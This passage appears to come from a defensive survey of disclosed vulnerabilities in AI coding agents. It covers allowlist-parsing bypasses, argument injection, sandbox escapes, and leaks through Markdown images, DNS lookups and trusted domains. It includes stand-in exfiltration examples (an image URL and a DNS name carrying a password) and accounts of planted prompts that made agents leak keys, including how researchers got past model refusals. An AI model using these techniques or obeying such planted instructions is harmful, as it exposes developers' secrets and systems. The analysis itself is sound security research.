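The remaining attack used `sed`, where an argument can be a small program. Such a program can write files and, in the GNU version common on Linux, run other programs, which RyotaK's attack did. Chester later got past a newer set of checks on `sed` expressions (CVE-2025-64755). One pattern matched the write command only when a space came before the file name, but `sed` doesn't need the space.

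On macOS, Chester used this to write to a file that the Zsh shell runs whenever it starts. The GitHub Advisory Database's *@anthropic-ai/claude-code has Sed Command Validation Bypass that Allows Arbitrary File Writes* (2025) mentions only writing files, but writing to that file is enough to run code. Anthropic released the fix on October 31, a week after Chester first emailed the company.

The two flaws disclosed on February 6 came from judging parts of a command line separately. The GitHub Advisory Database's *Claude Code Vulnerable to Command Injection via Directory Change Bypasses Write Protection* (2026) describes CVE-2026-25722, in which the line moved into a protected folder such as `.claude` and then wrote a file there. A file name like `settings.json` looks harmless if the software assumes the file is in the folder where the line started.

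In CVE-2026-25723, `echo` supplied text and `sed` wrote it to a protected folder or outside the project. According to the GitHub Advisory Database's *Claude Code Vulnerable to Command Injection via Piped sed Command* (2026), this worked only if the user had turned on "accept edits", a mode in which Claude Code changes project files without asking.

CVE-2026-24053 affected developers who used Zsh, the default shell on Macs. Claude Code's check was written for Bash. It incorrectly parsed Zsh's syntax for forcing an existing file to be overwritten, which let a command write outside the workspace, according to MITRE's *CVE-2026-24053* (2026).

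Anthropic has published much less about the other two. The GitHub Advisory Database's *Claude Code rg vulnerability does not protect against approval prompt bypass* (2025), which credits Nvidia's AI Red Team, attributes the `rg` flaw to "an error in command parsing". The database's *Claude Code has a Command Injection in find Command* (2026) describes the `find` flaw in the same words.

One of Chester's experiments suggests how the `find` check might have failed. Chester got a banned option past the pattern by putting quotation marks inside it. The shell would have removed the marks before starting `find`, but Claude Code's other checks caught the attempt in version 2.0.25, so the eventual flaw may have been different.

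### From blocking bad options to listing good ones

RyotaK reports that Anthropic responded to CVE-2025-66032 by replacing its blocklists with an allowlist. In Chester's slightly later copy of the program, the allowlist contained the acceptable options for each command and the kind of value each option takes, such as a number, text or nothing. The entry for `xargs` correctly recorded that `-t` takes no value. If the developers forget an option, such a list leads to an unnecessary question instead of an attack.

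The order in which the CVEs were published makes it hard to see how much the new approach achieved. Anthropic disclosed CVE-2025-66032 after the `rg` and `sed` flaws, but its version numbers show that it fixed CVE-2025-66032 first. Six flaws on the list, all except `echo` and CVE-2025-66032 itself, have later fixes, so they remained after the new approach was introduced. At least four of the six had little to do with a missing option and instead involved the `sed` language, the combination of two commands, a change of folder and Zsh syntax.

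In Manual mode, Claude Code now asks the user about any command it cannot fully analyse, which addresses this more directly. The rule depends on the software detecting when it has misread a command. Claude Code could analyse the `xargs` line in full, for example, and still got the wrong result.

### Gemini CLI and Codex on PowerShell

Commands in PowerShell, Microsoft's newer shell for Windows, are harder to check because PowerShell is also a full programming language. Gemini CLI had a check designed for PowerShell, but Ashkenazi and Tsukerman found that a bug made the agent always start the older Command Prompt instead. The software then only compared the beginning of a line with the allowlist. If the user had allowed `dir`, which lists files, any line that began with `dir` could include a second command.

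After Google's first fix, Gemini CLI used PowerShell's parser to turn the line into a syntax tree, a structured breakdown of its commands and expressions. It then checked every command in the tree against the allowlist, which caught a second command placed after `dir`.

But PowerShell can also call methods from .NET, Microsoft's programming platform, and the tree does not classify these calls as commands. A hijacked agent could use a method call to create a script and run it, while the check found only `dir`. The parser read the line correctly, but the code that searched the tree ignored everything except commands. A safer check would accept only kinds of syntax known to be harmless and ask the user about the rest.

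The Codex flaw, CVE-2026-19591, was a misreading of one PowerShell marker. Typing `--%` tells PowerShell to stop interpreting the line and pass the rest to the program more or less as written. Codex's check interpreted the marker differently and could therefore classify a Git command that writes a file as safe, according to MITRE's *CVE-2026-19591* (2026). This was the bug that Compass Security used against Codex at Pwn2Own Berlin. To turn it into code execution, an attacker needed several things to happen:

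1. The developer opens a project that the attacker prepared, and Codex follows the instructions in it.
2. Codex runs the Git command through PowerShell. Windows normally includes PowerShell, but a Mac or Linux user must have installed it separately.
3. The command changes Codex's settings.
4. Codex later loads those settings and starts the attacker's MCP server with the user's privileges.

The flaw skipped the approval prompt but left the sandbox on. If the settings are outside the places where Codex may write, the default sandbox on macOS and Linux can stop the attack by blocking the change. OpenAI does not give the same assurance for Windows in its record, and a developer who had turned the sandbox off would have had no such protection on any system.

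The flaw affected Codex CLI versions 0.72.0 to 0.130.0, and OpenAI fixed it in 0.131.0. The desktop app had the same flaw. According to the Zero Day Initiative's *(Pwn2Own) OpenAI Codex Improper Neutralization of Control Sequences Remote Code Execution Vulnerability* (2026), OpenAI received the report on June 2, 2026, and the advisory came out on September 10.

### Harmless names, harmful calls

An allowlist can still fail when the command line is parsed correctly if it approves a program by name and ignores what the options make it do. An attacker can keep the approved command and add options that change its effect, which security researchers call argument injection.

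Codex used to run five Git subcommands (`branch`, `status`, `log`, `diff` and `show`) without asking and outside the sandbox, on the assumption that they were harmless whatever their arguments. *GitPwned* (Fogel, 2026) disproved this with `git show`, which normally displays a saved change to the project. One option makes the command write to a file, and another lets the caller choose the text it writes.

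A hijacked agent could use both options to rewrite the project's Git settings and name a program for Git to use when comparing files. Git would then run that program the next time the developer ran `git diff`. In Fogel's demonstration, Codex asked before running `curl`, which contacts web addresses, but ran the harmful `git show` without asking.

Staff at Bugcrowd, which handled the report for OpenAI, could not reproduce the attack at first because the model refused to follow the planted text. Fogel replied that the model might refuse nine times and comply on the tenth, and that nothing else in Codex would then stop the command. According to Fogel, the underlying error is treating commands as inherently safe or dangerous, when their safety depends on how they are invoked.

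OpenAI fixed the flaw in version 0.95.0 on February 4, 2026, four weeks after the report. According to Mend.io's *WS-2026-0013* (2026), Codex now inspects Git's arguments and any settings supplied on the command line, and asks for approval unless the command only reads data. The fix also covers options that start external programs and destructive uses of other Git commands. Mend.io lists no CVE for the flaw. Once Codex relied on Git's arguments, it had to interpret them correctly, and the PowerShell flaw caused it to misread them.

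Google's Antigravity had a similar problem in its file-search tool, which most users would not expect to run commands. The tool passes the agent's search pattern to a program called `fd`. Lisichkin (2026), in *Prompt Injection leads to RCE and Sandbox Escape in Antigravity*, found that `fd` treated a pattern beginning with a hyphen as an option. One of `fd`'s options starts a program on the files that the search finds. The agent could, without approval, create a file containing the attacker's commands and then run them by searching for the file with that option.

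The attack worked even in Secure Mode, Antigravity's strictest setting, which is supposed to run all commands in a sandbox. Antigravity classed the search as a built-in tool instead of a shell command, so Secure Mode did not restrict it. Lisichkin reported the flaw on January 7, 2026, and Google marked it as fixed on February 28.

The standard defence in this case is to put two hyphens by themselves before the data, because many programs treat anything after them as plain data rather than options. Antigravity did not put the hyphens before the pattern or check the pattern for unexpected characters.

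### Would another approach work better?

Denylists, which block bad commands instead of approving good ones, are probably the weakest option. Chen and Lin collected 1,709 denylists from projects on GitHub, used a language model to suggest other commands with the same effects as the blocked ones, and ran the suggestions in a sandbox to check their effects. Between 69.0% and 98.6% of the lists failed to fully block an operation they were meant to block.

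One list stopped six common programs from displaying files that often hold passwords, but the ordinary command for copying files could also display them. A list aimed at specific operations would need 217 more commands on average to be complete. The study covered only file operations, so it doesn't measure how well such lists block network access.

Vendors make the same mistake. Claude Code's automatic mode has a built-in list of programs that can run arbitrary code, such as Python and Bash. A user's allowlist cannot approve these programs, and a second model has to review them. Chen and Lin found that the list omitted `awk`, which is mainly a text-processing tool but can start a shell and is included in almost every Unix-like system.

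A stricter allowlist fails more safely because the agent asks the user before running any unlisted command. But it is hard to decide what to list. Trail of Bits' *Prompt injection to RCE in AI agents* (2025) points out that blocking all arguments would break essential functions, while filtering them requires knowing every option of every program. A short list helps, especially if it leaves out programs with their own languages. Chester suggests that researchers look next at `jq`, a JSON processor with its own language.

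For Codex, Fogel considered removing Git from the list or blocking particular options. Removing Git would close the gap but interrupt developers constantly. Blocking options by name could repeat Claude Code's mistake with `--upload-pa`, unless the filter also recognises abbreviations. Cohen recommends judging the whole call, including its arguments, the folder, the current settings and the possible side effects. Those are the right things to check, but checking them accurately would require reproducing much of each listed program's behaviour.

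The agent could also start a program directly, without a shell, and pass it a list of separate arguments. Quotation marks, semicolons and variables would then lose their special meanings. This would have prevented the `echo` and Zsh flaws and RyotaK's attacks with variables. It would also have prevented the Codex flaw if Codex had started Git directly instead of through PowerShell.

But developers often need a shell, for example to send one program's output to another, and removing it doesn't block dangerous options. In Antigravity, `fd` treated spaces in the injected text as ordinary characters, which suggests that no shell was interpreting them, yet the injected option still worked.

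Asking users to approve more commands avoids the need to predict what each command does, but people already tire of approval prompts. Chen and Lin cite data showing that users approve 93% of requests. Most requests are presumably legitimate, so that figure doesn't measure how many approvals were mistakes, but a person who almost always says yes is likely to miss a rare bad command. Having a second model review commands avoids this fatigue, but Chen and Lin note that attackers can mislead that model too.

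Lisichkin argues that vendors should isolate the execution of commands instead of relying on sanitizing them. A sandbox is the best of these remedies for parsing errors because it doesn't have to interpret commands. But Ashkenazi and Tsukerman found that allowlisted commands usually run outside the sandbox, so one mistake in the list removes both the approval prompt and the sandbox's restrictions, as happened with `git show`.

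Vendors can avoid this by using the allowlist only to skip the approval prompt and running every command in the sandbox, including commands that built-in tools start. The sandbox also has to protect sensitive files inside the project, such as `.git/config`. If a sandbox had allowed writes anywhere in the workspace, `git show` could still have rewritten that file, and the developer's own `git diff` would later have run the attacker's program outside the sandbox.

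## What do sandboxes stop, and how were they crossed?

A sandbox's limits apply to a command and any program the command starts, including a build script or downloaded package that nobody inspected. Researchers have found many ways past these limits, mostly by getting a program outside the sandbox to do what the sandbox blocks.

### How the limits work on Linux and macOS

On Linux, Claude Code and current versions of Codex run commands through a program called bubblewrap. It relies on namespaces, a feature of the kernel (the core of the operating system) that gives a process its own view of the files, the network or another part of the machine. Codex builds the view of the files in layers, called mounts:

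1. It mounts the whole disk read-only.
2. It mounts the workspace again on top, this time writable.
3. It mounts protected folders inside the workspace, such as `.git` and `.codex`, read-only again.

A command that tries to write outside the permitted locations gets an error from the kernel. *OpenAI Codex CLI Sandbox Implementation Analysis* (Willison, 2025) describes an earlier Linux design for Codex that achieved a similar result with two other kernel features. Landlock restricted file access, and seccomp blocked the system calls that open network connections.

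Claude Code's sandboxed commands on Linux also get a network namespace with no outside connection. According to Anthropic, they can reach only a proxy, a go-between program outside the sandbox that checks each requested hostname against the allowed domains. Most database clients don't use the proxy, so they can't connect even to an allowed host.

On macOS, the products use Apple's Seatbelt. The vendor writes a list of rules, called a profile, and the kernel checks the process's requests against it. The process doesn't get a separate view of the files. A profile can deny everything by default and list what the process may do, or allow everything by default and list exceptions. In *The Week of Sandbox Escapes Day 1*, Lisichkin (2026) calls Seatbelt "isolation by promise" because the protection is only as good as the profile.

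The two systems also differ in when they apply a rule. Anthropic offers a separate package, the sandbox runtime, that puts a whole program under the same kind of limits. According to Anthropic's *Choose a sandbox environment*, on macOS the runtime applies its rules at each write, so they also protect the Git settings of a repository that the agent creates during the session. On Linux, the runtime lists the protected files once, at launch, so files created later aren't protected.

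Many developers have none of this protection. Claude Code's sandbox is off until the user turns it on, and on Windows it works only through the Windows Subsystem for Linux. If the sandbox can't start, for example because bubblewrap is missing, Claude Code by default runs commands unsandboxed.

### Why much of the agent stays outside

Claude Code can rely on permission rules instead of the sandbox to limit its file tools, because each tool performs one defined operation, such as writing text to a given path. A shell command can start any program on the machine, so it needs operating system limits more than the file tools do. MCP servers and hooks also run outside the sandbox, and some are hard to confine, such as an MCP server that must reach a database on the same computer.

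The program outside the sandbox can also make exceptions. When the sandbox causes a command to fail, the model may ask Claude Code to rerun it unsandboxed. In Manual mode, Claude Code asks the user to approve this, unless the user has already allowed that command, since that permission also covers unsandboxed runs. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* acknowledges that a persuasive planted prompt or a tired user's approval can therefore let a command run outside the sandbox without any flaw in the software.

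### Codex let the model choose the boundary

When a model runs a command through Codex, it can specify the folder where the command starts, for example to run tests in part of a project. In versions 0.2.0 to 0.38.0, Codex could use that folder as the sandbox's writable area, even if it was outside the folder where the user had started the session. A hijacked model could specify the user's home folder, and the operating system, which enforces the sandbox, would then let the command write there.

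OSV's *CVE-2025-59532* (2025), a record in a database of open-source vulnerabilities, rates the flaw's severity at 8.6. The sandbox still blocked network access, so a command inside it could change the user's files but not send them anywhere. OpenAI's fix in version 0.39.0 resolves the path and bases the sandbox boundary on where the user started the session. Users of the editor extension needed version 0.4.12.

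Cursor disclosed nearly the same mistake nine months later. According to Lutra Security's *Cursor Desktop sandbox escape via agent-controlled working directory* (2026), Cursor gave each command write access to that command's working folder, and the agent could set the folder to a sensitive location. An attacker could overwrite Cursor's sandbox helper program this way. Cursor fixed the flaw in version 3.0. The Windsurf flaw in which a README redefined the workspace was a cruder form of the same error. A model may need to choose the folder where a command starts, but that choice shouldn't affect where the command can write.

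### Three escapes from Claude Code

CVE-2026-25725 allowed malicious code to escape Claude Code's Linux sandbox by creating a missing settings file. The sandbox made the project's `.claude` folder writable and protected `settings.local.json` inside it with a read-only mount, but it protected `settings.json` only if the file existed at startup. According to GitLab's *CVE-2026-25725* (2026), code in the sandbox could create `settings.json` and add a hook to it. When the user next started Claude Code, the hook ran outside the sandbox with the user's full access.

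Anthropic fixed the flaw in version 2.1.2. Claude Code now protects a missing file on Linux by putting an empty, read-only placeholder in its place while a sandboxed command runs. But if something kills the session before Claude Code removes the placeholder, later sessions can't save settings there. CERT.hr's *CVE-2026-25725* lists the severity as 10.0, while OSV's *CVE-2026-25725* (2026) lists 7.7 under a newer version of CVSS.

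Exploiting CVE-2026-39861 took one step inside Claude Code's sandbox and one outside it. A sandboxed command could create a symlink in the workspace that pointed to a folder elsewhere. The command couldn't write through the link, because the operating system would have blocked the write at its real destination. But Claude Code ran outside the sandbox, so when it later wrote to a path through the link, the data landed outside the workspace without an approval prompt.

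NVD's *CVE-2026-39861 Detail* notes that neither the sandboxed command nor Claude Code could have made that write outside the workspace alone. Claude Code's rules should have kept the write inside the workspace, but they didn't account for a link that a sandboxed command had just made. The flaw has the same two scores as CVE-2026-25725, according to OSV's *GHSA-vp62-r36r-9xqp* (2026). Anthropic fixed it in version 2.1.64 but didn't publish the method. The later CVE-2026-88968, in which sandboxed code on macOS could redirect a file edit, suggests that the fix left at least one similar route open.

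CVE-2026-55607 involved Git worktrees, which are extra copies of a project that let a developer work on two branches at once. Git normally keeps a project's history and settings in a folder called `.git`. Claude Code allowed a worktree to be named `.git`, so ordinary project files could sit where Git expected its own data. It also let the agent move to worktrees outside the sandbox.

An attacker could combine this confusion with symlinks and a Git setting that starts a program. According to GitLab's *CVE-2026-55607* (2026), this let the attacker overwrite a Zsh startup file such as `.zshenv` and so run code outside the sandbox. The attack worked only if the developer downloaded a malicious project containing planted instructions and ran Claude Code on it. The flaw affected versions from 2.1.38 until the fix in 2.1.163 and had a severity score of 8.8.

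Claude Code's current sandbox has several rules against this kind of confusion. In a worktree, commands can write to the main project's shared Git folder, which they need to save changes, but not to that folder's settings or hooks. On Linux, the sandbox also deletes certain newly created files that would make the workspace itself look like Git's data folder.

### Pillar Security's seven findings

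Pillar Security's July 2026 series, which includes the attacks on Cursor's Python extension and hooks, covers seven findings in four products. Cohen and colleagues sort the findings into four types of failure: sandboxes that list what to forbid, project settings that work as code, allowlists that approve commands by name, and background services outside the sandbox.

| Finding | Product | Type of failure | Outcome |
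|---|---|---|---|
| Seatbelt profile that allows by default | Antigravity | List of forbidden actions | Google accepted the report but downgraded it |
| Docker service within reach | Codex, Cursor, Gemini CLI | Background service | Only Cursor issued a fix for the report |
| Replaced Python interpreter | Cursor | Settings as code | CVE-2026-73217, fixed in 3.1.2 |
| Git data under another name | Cursor | Settings as code | Fixed in 3.0.0 |
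| Hook file | Cursor | Settings as code | CVE-2026-48124, fixed in 3.0.0 |
| Editor task | Antigravity | Settings as code | Google accepted the report but downgraded it |
| `git show` with harmful options | Codex | Allowlist by name | Fixed in 0.95.0 |

Antigravity's Seatbelt profile allowed everything by default, so its developers had to anticipate and forbid every dangerous operation in macOS, and they missed one. macOS marks files that a sandboxed process creates, and the service that opens applications won't start a program with that mark. Lisichkin used the missed operation to build a program without the mark, which the service then started outside the sandbox.

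The attack worked only with Antigravity's Secure Mode off, its terminal sandbox on and commands set to run without approval. Secure Mode is on by default, which supports Google's view that the flaw is hard to exploit. But Lisichkin notes that people who turn on a sandbox often do so to stop approving commands. Lisichkin recommends a profile that denies by default, although it takes longer to write and tends to break things at first.

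Codex, Cursor and Gemini CLI had sandbox profiles that limited what the agent's own process could write. In *The Week of Sandbox Escapes Day 2*, Lisichkin (2026) got past them through Docker Desktop, a common program for running containers. Docker has a background service that accepts requests through a socket, a connection point for programs on the same machine. The agent could use this socket to have the service start a container with access to the user's home folder. The sandbox's rules didn't stop the writing because the service did it, not the agent's process.

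The attack required network access, because macOS treats a connection to the socket as a network operation. Cursor rated the flaw high severity and fixed it. OpenAI paid for the report and agreed the behaviour was unintended, but classed it as informational and declined to issue a CVE. It said Codex now denies access to such sockets unless the user allows it. Google's Gemini CLI team said its documentation already covered the risk.

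OpenAI can reasonably argue that this was not an escape from the default sandbox, since network access is off unless the user enables it. But a developer who turns on the network to download packages wouldn't expect that to also give the agent write access to the home folder. Cursor served users in that position better by deciding to fix the flaw.

### How well do Pillar's claims hold up?

Pillar sells a product that monitors agents on developers' machines, so it benefits when sandboxes look weak. But the official records support its main findings about Cursor. NVD's *CVE-2026-73218 Detail* (2026), for example, confirms that the Docker attack gave an agent access to the home folder and let it run commands with the user's privileges. The record gives the flaw a score of 7.7 and lists version 3.0.0 as the fix.

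The record also limits the claim to machines with Docker Desktop and another tool, the Dev Containers CLI. Lisichkin says Docker Desktop is on nearly every Mac that runs these agents, but gives no figures. The summary table by Cohen and colleagues marks the Docker issue as fixed for all three products, and Techzine, a technology news site, repeated this. But according to Lisichkin's detailed account, only Cursor treated the report as a flaw to fix.

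Lisichkin argues more broadly that a sandbox sharing the computer's kernel is the wrong design for agents. The seven findings don't establish this, because none involved exploiting a kernel flaw. They depended on what the vendor allowed the agent to reach and on how other programs handled what the agent produced.

### A confined writer and a trusting reader

The flaws in Claude Code and Codex also fit Pillar's pattern, in which a program outside the sandbox acts on something that a process inside it was allowed to produce. That output is often a file, but it can also be a request or a value in a tool call.

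| Flaw | What came from the confined side | What acted on it |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Code, CVE-2026-25725 | A settings file containing a hook | Claude Code, at its next start |
| Claude Code, CVE-2026-39861 | A symlink | Claude Code, when writing a file |
| Claude Code, CVE-2026-55607 | Misplaced project files and symlinks | Git, during worktree operations |
| Codex, CVE-2025-59532 | The name of a working folder | The code that set up the sandbox |
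| Antigravity, Seatbelt profile | A program without the usual mark | The macOS service that opens applications |
| Cursor, CVE-2026-73218 | A request for a container | The Docker service |

In versions of Cursor before 2.5, a sandboxed agent could write to a project's Git settings, including hooks that Git later ran outside the sandbox, according to Enginsight's *CVE-2026-26268*.

One remedy is to stop the confined process from writing anything that an unconfined program will treat as instructions. The sandbox in Claude Code now blocks commands from changing Claude Code's settings, MCP configuration and hooks, Git's settings and hooks, and anything in the `.vscode` folder. Users can't exempt individual files. They can remove the protection only by turning off all of the sandbox's file limits, which a project's own settings can't do.

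This list of protected files, like others, can be incomplete. Anthropic's documentation doesn't include Python environments among the protected paths, for instance, so an editor extension that runs a project's interpreter could remain exposed. The other remedy, which Cohen and colleagues recommend, is to confine the program that reads the files too.

### What a working sandbox prevents

The sandboxes still offer protection despite these flaws. A sandboxed command normally can't change the user's shell startup files or system programs, and it can't download malware from an unapproved domain. The same limits apply to a malicious npm package that the agent installs by mistake. To escape, an attacker has to find a specific flaw and may then have to wait for another event, such as a restart.

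In an internal exercise at Anthropic in February 2026, a researcher persuaded a colleague by email to give Claude Code a prompt that looked like routine setup work but included an instruction to send out the colleague's Amazon login keys. Claude sent the keys in 24 of 25 attempts. A classifier had little to detect, because the instruction came from the user. Blocking either the network destination or access to the keys would have stopped the attack.

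By default, only the network limit would help with shell commands in such a case. Claude Code's sandbox lets commands read almost the whole disk, including files that hold passwords and keys, unless the user blocks access to them. The network limit is also incomplete. The proxy allows or blocks a connection based on its hostname and doesn't normally inspect encrypted traffic, so commands can send data out through an approved site that accepts uploads, such as GitHub.

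Anthropic's description of its sandbox has become more cautious. *Beyond permission prompts*, which announced the feature, said that "even a successful prompt injection is fully isolated". The company's current documentation says that sandboxing "is not a complete isolation boundary". The announcement also reported that sandboxing cut approval prompts by 84% in the company's internal use. Fewer prompts may help people pay attention to the ones that remain, but a command that escapes the sandbox may have run without anyone seeing it first.

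### What a container or virtual machine adds

A developer can instead confine the whole agent. Anthropic's sandbox runtime does this without a container, putting the file tools, MCP servers and hooks under the same limits as shell commands. If the boundary is set correctly, the symlink attack in CVE-2026-39861 would fail, because neither Claude Code nor its shell commands could write outside the workspace. But Claude Code needs to write to its own settings folder, so the developer has to protect the sensitive files there separately. Otherwise a hijacked session could leave a hook that runs the next time the developer starts Claude Code without the runtime.

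A container gives the agent its own set of files, and the agent can see only the folders on the host computer that the developer shares. It takes more work to set up and still shares the host's kernel. A virtual machine has its own kernel, so it offers the strongest separation, but Anthropic rates its setup effort as high. Some virtual machines include their own Docker service, which lets an agent use containers without reaching the Docker service on the developer's computer.

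Anthropic found other drawbacks when it built Claude Cowork, an agent for general office work that originally ran entirely inside a virtual machine. If the virtual machine failed to start, the whole product stopped working. Anthropic moved the agent's main program outside so that it could still respond, but kept code execution inside. It also moved local MCP servers out, partly because some needed other programs on the user's computer. Companies also complained that their security software couldn't monitor what happened inside the virtual machine. Anthropic lets administrators retrieve event logs afterwards, but these don't provide live monitoring.

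A virtual machine also can't stop data from leaving through an approved connection. Cowork's network rules allowed connections to Anthropic's servers because Cowork needed them to work. An outside researcher planted a file with hidden instructions and an attacker's access key, and Claude used the key to upload the user's files to the attacker's Anthropic account. Anthropic responded by adding a proxy that accepts only the session's own credentials.

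The shared project folder also remains a risk, because an editor on the host computer may later run a malicious task or Python interpreter that the agent left there. Anthropic advises that, after an unattended run, users review the folders they left writable.

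## How does private data leave through displayed text and routine requests?

A sandbox can stop a shell command from contacting an attacker's server, but the chat window that displays the agent's reply may still contact it. Chat windows usually format replies with Markdown, a simple notation for headings, links and images. A reply includes an image by giving its web address, and the chat window requests the picture from the server at that address. The server receives the whole address, including any private text the model put in it.

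Suppose a project's settings file contains the dummy password `teal-42`, and somebody has planted instructions in a comment in the source code.

1. A developer asks the agent to explain the code. The model reads the comment and follows it.
2. The agent opens the settings file. The file is inside the workspace, so no approval prompt appears.
3. The model starts its reply with an image whose address is `pictures.example/dot.png?v=teal-42`, then explains the code as usual.
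4. The chat window requests the image. The attacker's server returns a transparent dot and records the address, which includes the password.

The agent never requested network access, so the software had no request to check. The JSON schema leak worked in much the same way.

*16th June 2024* (Willison, 2024) gives the general rule that a chat interface has this flaw if it handles both private and untrusted data and displays Markdown images. The attack is older than most coding agents. *14th April 2023* (Willison, 2023) describes Roman Samoilenko's demonstration of it against ChatGPT and notes that mitigation began only in December 2023.

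### Copilot Chat and Cursor's diagrams

In February 2024, Rehberger reported the flaw in the Copilot Chat extension for VS Code. Embrace The Red's *GitHub Copilot Chat* shows how text planted in a source file made the model add codes and names from earlier in the conversation to an image address. GitHub replied that it was already tracking the bug, and it confirmed a fix on June 12.

Accounts of that fix differ. Rehberger thought the extension had stopped displaying all Markdown images, while Willison wrote that GitHub had blocked only images from untrusted domains. Vulners' *Source Code and data exfiltration via Github Copilot* also mentions trusted domains, along with a warning before the user opens a link, but it is undated and may describe a different report. If GitHub blocked only untrusted domains, data could still leak through any trusted site that can pass it to an attacker.

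VerSprite's *Another Day, Another Leak* describes the same problem in CodeGPT, another VS Code extension, and criticises the vendor for not acting.

Cursor had a less obvious version of the flaw, which involved its ability to draw diagrams from Mermaid, a text format for flowcharts and similar figures. Rehberger found that a diagram could include an image from an outside server. Embrace The Red describes two demonstrations in which a hijacked agent leaked API keys from a configuration file and the "memories" that Cursor had stored about the user. The finished diagram appeared all at once, so the user had no chance to notice private data in the text behind it.

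This flaw is CVE-2025-54132, and MITRE's *Cursor's Mermaid Diagram Tool is Vulnerable to an Arbitrary Image Fetch* (2025) scores it 4.4 (medium). Cursor resolved it within a week of the June 30 report and released the fix in version 1.3 on July 29.

In October, Cursor disclosed CVE-2025-61589, the same kind of leak in versions up to 1.6. CVELogic's *CVE-2025-61589* mentions further bypasses that the initial fix did not cover, and SentinelOne's *CVE-2025-61589* lists 1.7 as the fixed version.

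### CamoLeak

GitHub's website also has an assistant called Copilot Chat, which answers questions about code, issues and pull requests. In June 2025, Omer Mayraz of the security company Legit Security found a way to steal private code through it. The company published the attack as CamoLeak in October.

Legit Security's *CamoLeak* describes an attack in which the attacker puts instructions in a pull request's description using hidden comments, an official GitHub feature. The project's owner gets the usual notification, but it does not show the hidden text. When any user asks Copilot about the pull request, Copilot reads the comment. It works with that user's permissions, so the instructions can direct it to the user's private repositories.

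Mayraz first had Copilot put the stolen data in a link, but the victim had to click it. An image would load without a click, but GitHub's content security policy, which lists the sites from which the browser may load a page's content, blocked images from outside GitHub.

Project pages can still show outside pictures because GitHub loads them through its own image proxy, Camo:

1. When somebody saves a README containing an outside image, GitHub replaces the image's address with a Camo address that includes a cryptographic signature.
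2. The reader's browser requests the Camo address, which the policy allows.
3. Camo checks the signature. If GitHub created it, Camo fetches the picture from the outside server and passes it on.

The model cannot create a valid signature, so it cannot write a new Camo address that contains a password. CamoLeak instead used only addresses that GitHub had already signed. Mayraz had GitHub sign one image address for each letter and symbol, then included the whole set in the planted text, along with instructions for Copilot to spell out the private data as a row of these images.

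To leak the word `teal`, for example, Copilot would display the images for t, e, a and l. Camo would accept their valid signatures and fetch each image, and the attacker could read the word from the order of the requests. Each image was a single transparent pixel, so the user saw nothing. Copilot also added a random number to each address so that a repeated letter would trigger a new request instead of loading from the cache.

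The signatures limited which addresses Camo would fetch, but a page could request them in any order. Sending one request per character is slow for a large file but fast enough for a key. Mayraz used this method to steal the description of an unpublished vulnerability from a private project. In another test, Copilot searched the victim's code for "AWS_KEY" and leaked the result.

By August 14, 2025, GitHub had fixed the flaw by disabling all images in Copilot Chat. Petri's *GitHub Copilot Chat Hit by ‘CamoLeak’ Flaw Allowing Silent Data Exfiltration* reports that GitHub also blocked this use of Camo. Disabling images is more dependable because it works even if another permitted site could relay requests the same way.

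CamoLeak appears to have no CVE number. Legit Security gives it a severity score of 9.6 but no CVE number. VPN Central's *Hackers exploited GitHub Copilot flaw to exfiltrate sensitive data from private repositories* lists it as CVE-2025-59145, but MITRE's *color-name@2.0.1 contains malware after npm account takeover* (2025) shows that this number belongs to unrelated malware in an npm package.

### Name lookups in Claude Code

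In CVE-2025-55284, Claude Code leaked data without displaying any images. The data left through the Domain Name System (DNS), which computers use to find a server's numerical address from its name. A lookup passes from one DNS server to another until it reaches the one responsible for the domain. If an attacker runs that server for `collector.example`, a lookup of `teal-42.collector.example` gives them the password `teal-42`. The victim's computer doesn't have to connect to the attacker's website.

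Claude Code's allowlist included `ping`, `nslookup`, `host` and `dig`, network diagnostic commands that can look up domain names. Rehberger found the list in the program's code and asked Claude which entries an attacker could misuse, and Claude identified these four.

Embrace The Red describes a demonstration in which planted text made the agent read an API key from a `.env` file and ping a domain name containing the key. Claude refused direct instructions to do this, so Rehberger used text-search commands to disguise the purpose. Claude also refused to contact domains known for security testing but accepted an ordinary one.

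OSV's *Claude Code's Permissive Default Allowlist Enables Unauthorized File Read and Network Exfiltration* (2025) attributes the flaw to an overly broad allowlist. The four commands normally change nothing on the machine, but they send text to other computers. Rehberger recommended removing them from the list. Anthropic reported a fix 11 days after receiving the report and released the fix in version 1.0.4.

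### Approved websites

Claude Code also has a tool for reading web pages, WebFetch, which could open certain trusted sites, such as Python's documentation, without asking. According to MITRE's *Claude Code has a Domain Validation Bypass* (2026), the software checked only whether an address began with a trusted name.

Claude Code skipped the approval prompt for web addresses that began with the name of a trusted site. But the end of a domain name determines who controls it, so the owner of `example.com` can create `modelcontextprotocol.io.example.com` and point it to any server. A hijacked agent could therefore send private data to an attacker in an ordinary page request without the user's approval. Anthropic fixed this flaw, CVE-2026-24052, in version 1.0.111. It resembles the mistake that let Claude Code treat `shop-private` as part of `shop`. A safe check extracts the hostname from the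 address and compares all of it with the approved name.

In CVE-2026-54316, WebFetch trusted every page on `huggingface.co`, where people, including attackers, can publish AI models and data. When the agent requested certain files from an attacker's repository, Hugging Face counted each request as a download. Checking the whole hostname would not have prevented this, because the attacker's repository was on the trusted site.

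The attacker could use those counts to receive data. For instance, each of several repositories could stand for a different letter or number, like the images in CamoLeak. Hugging Face's counter worked normally, and the agent contacted only the approved site.

MITRE lists the affected versions as 0.2.54 up to 2.1.163, which fixed the flaw, and notes that the approval applied even when the user had restricted the agent's tools. GitLab's *CVE-2026-54316* (2026) credits the security company Novee. Neither source explains how Anthropic fixed the flaw; it could have removed Hugging Face from the approved list or approved only pages where an attacker cannot publish.

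### A project setting that redirected the API key

CVE-2026-21852 required no prompt injection. Claude Code sends requests to Anthropic with an API key, a secret that identifies the account to bill. The `ANTHROPIC_BASE_URL` setting determines which server receives the requests, and a project could set it in its `.claude/settings.json` file.

A project's settings can choose which server receives Claude Code's requests. In *Caught in the Hook*, Donenfeld and Vanunu (2026) used this setting to route the requests through a program that let them inspect the traffic. Claude Code sent several requests before they could answer the dialog asking whether they trusted the project. Each request included the full API key, and some appeared to include file names and recent commit messages. An attacker could therefore publish a project that set this to their own server, and a developer who downloaded the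 project and started Claude Code in it would send the attacker their key.

A stolen key can expose more than the developer's own work. Anthropic's developer console has shared areas called Workspaces, which are separate from the project folders on a developer's machine. Every key in a Workspace gives access to the files stored there. Users could not download files they had uploaded, but Donenfeld and Vanunu got around this by asking Claude to make a copy, which they could download. An attacker could also delete a team's files, fill its 100 GB of storage or run up charges.

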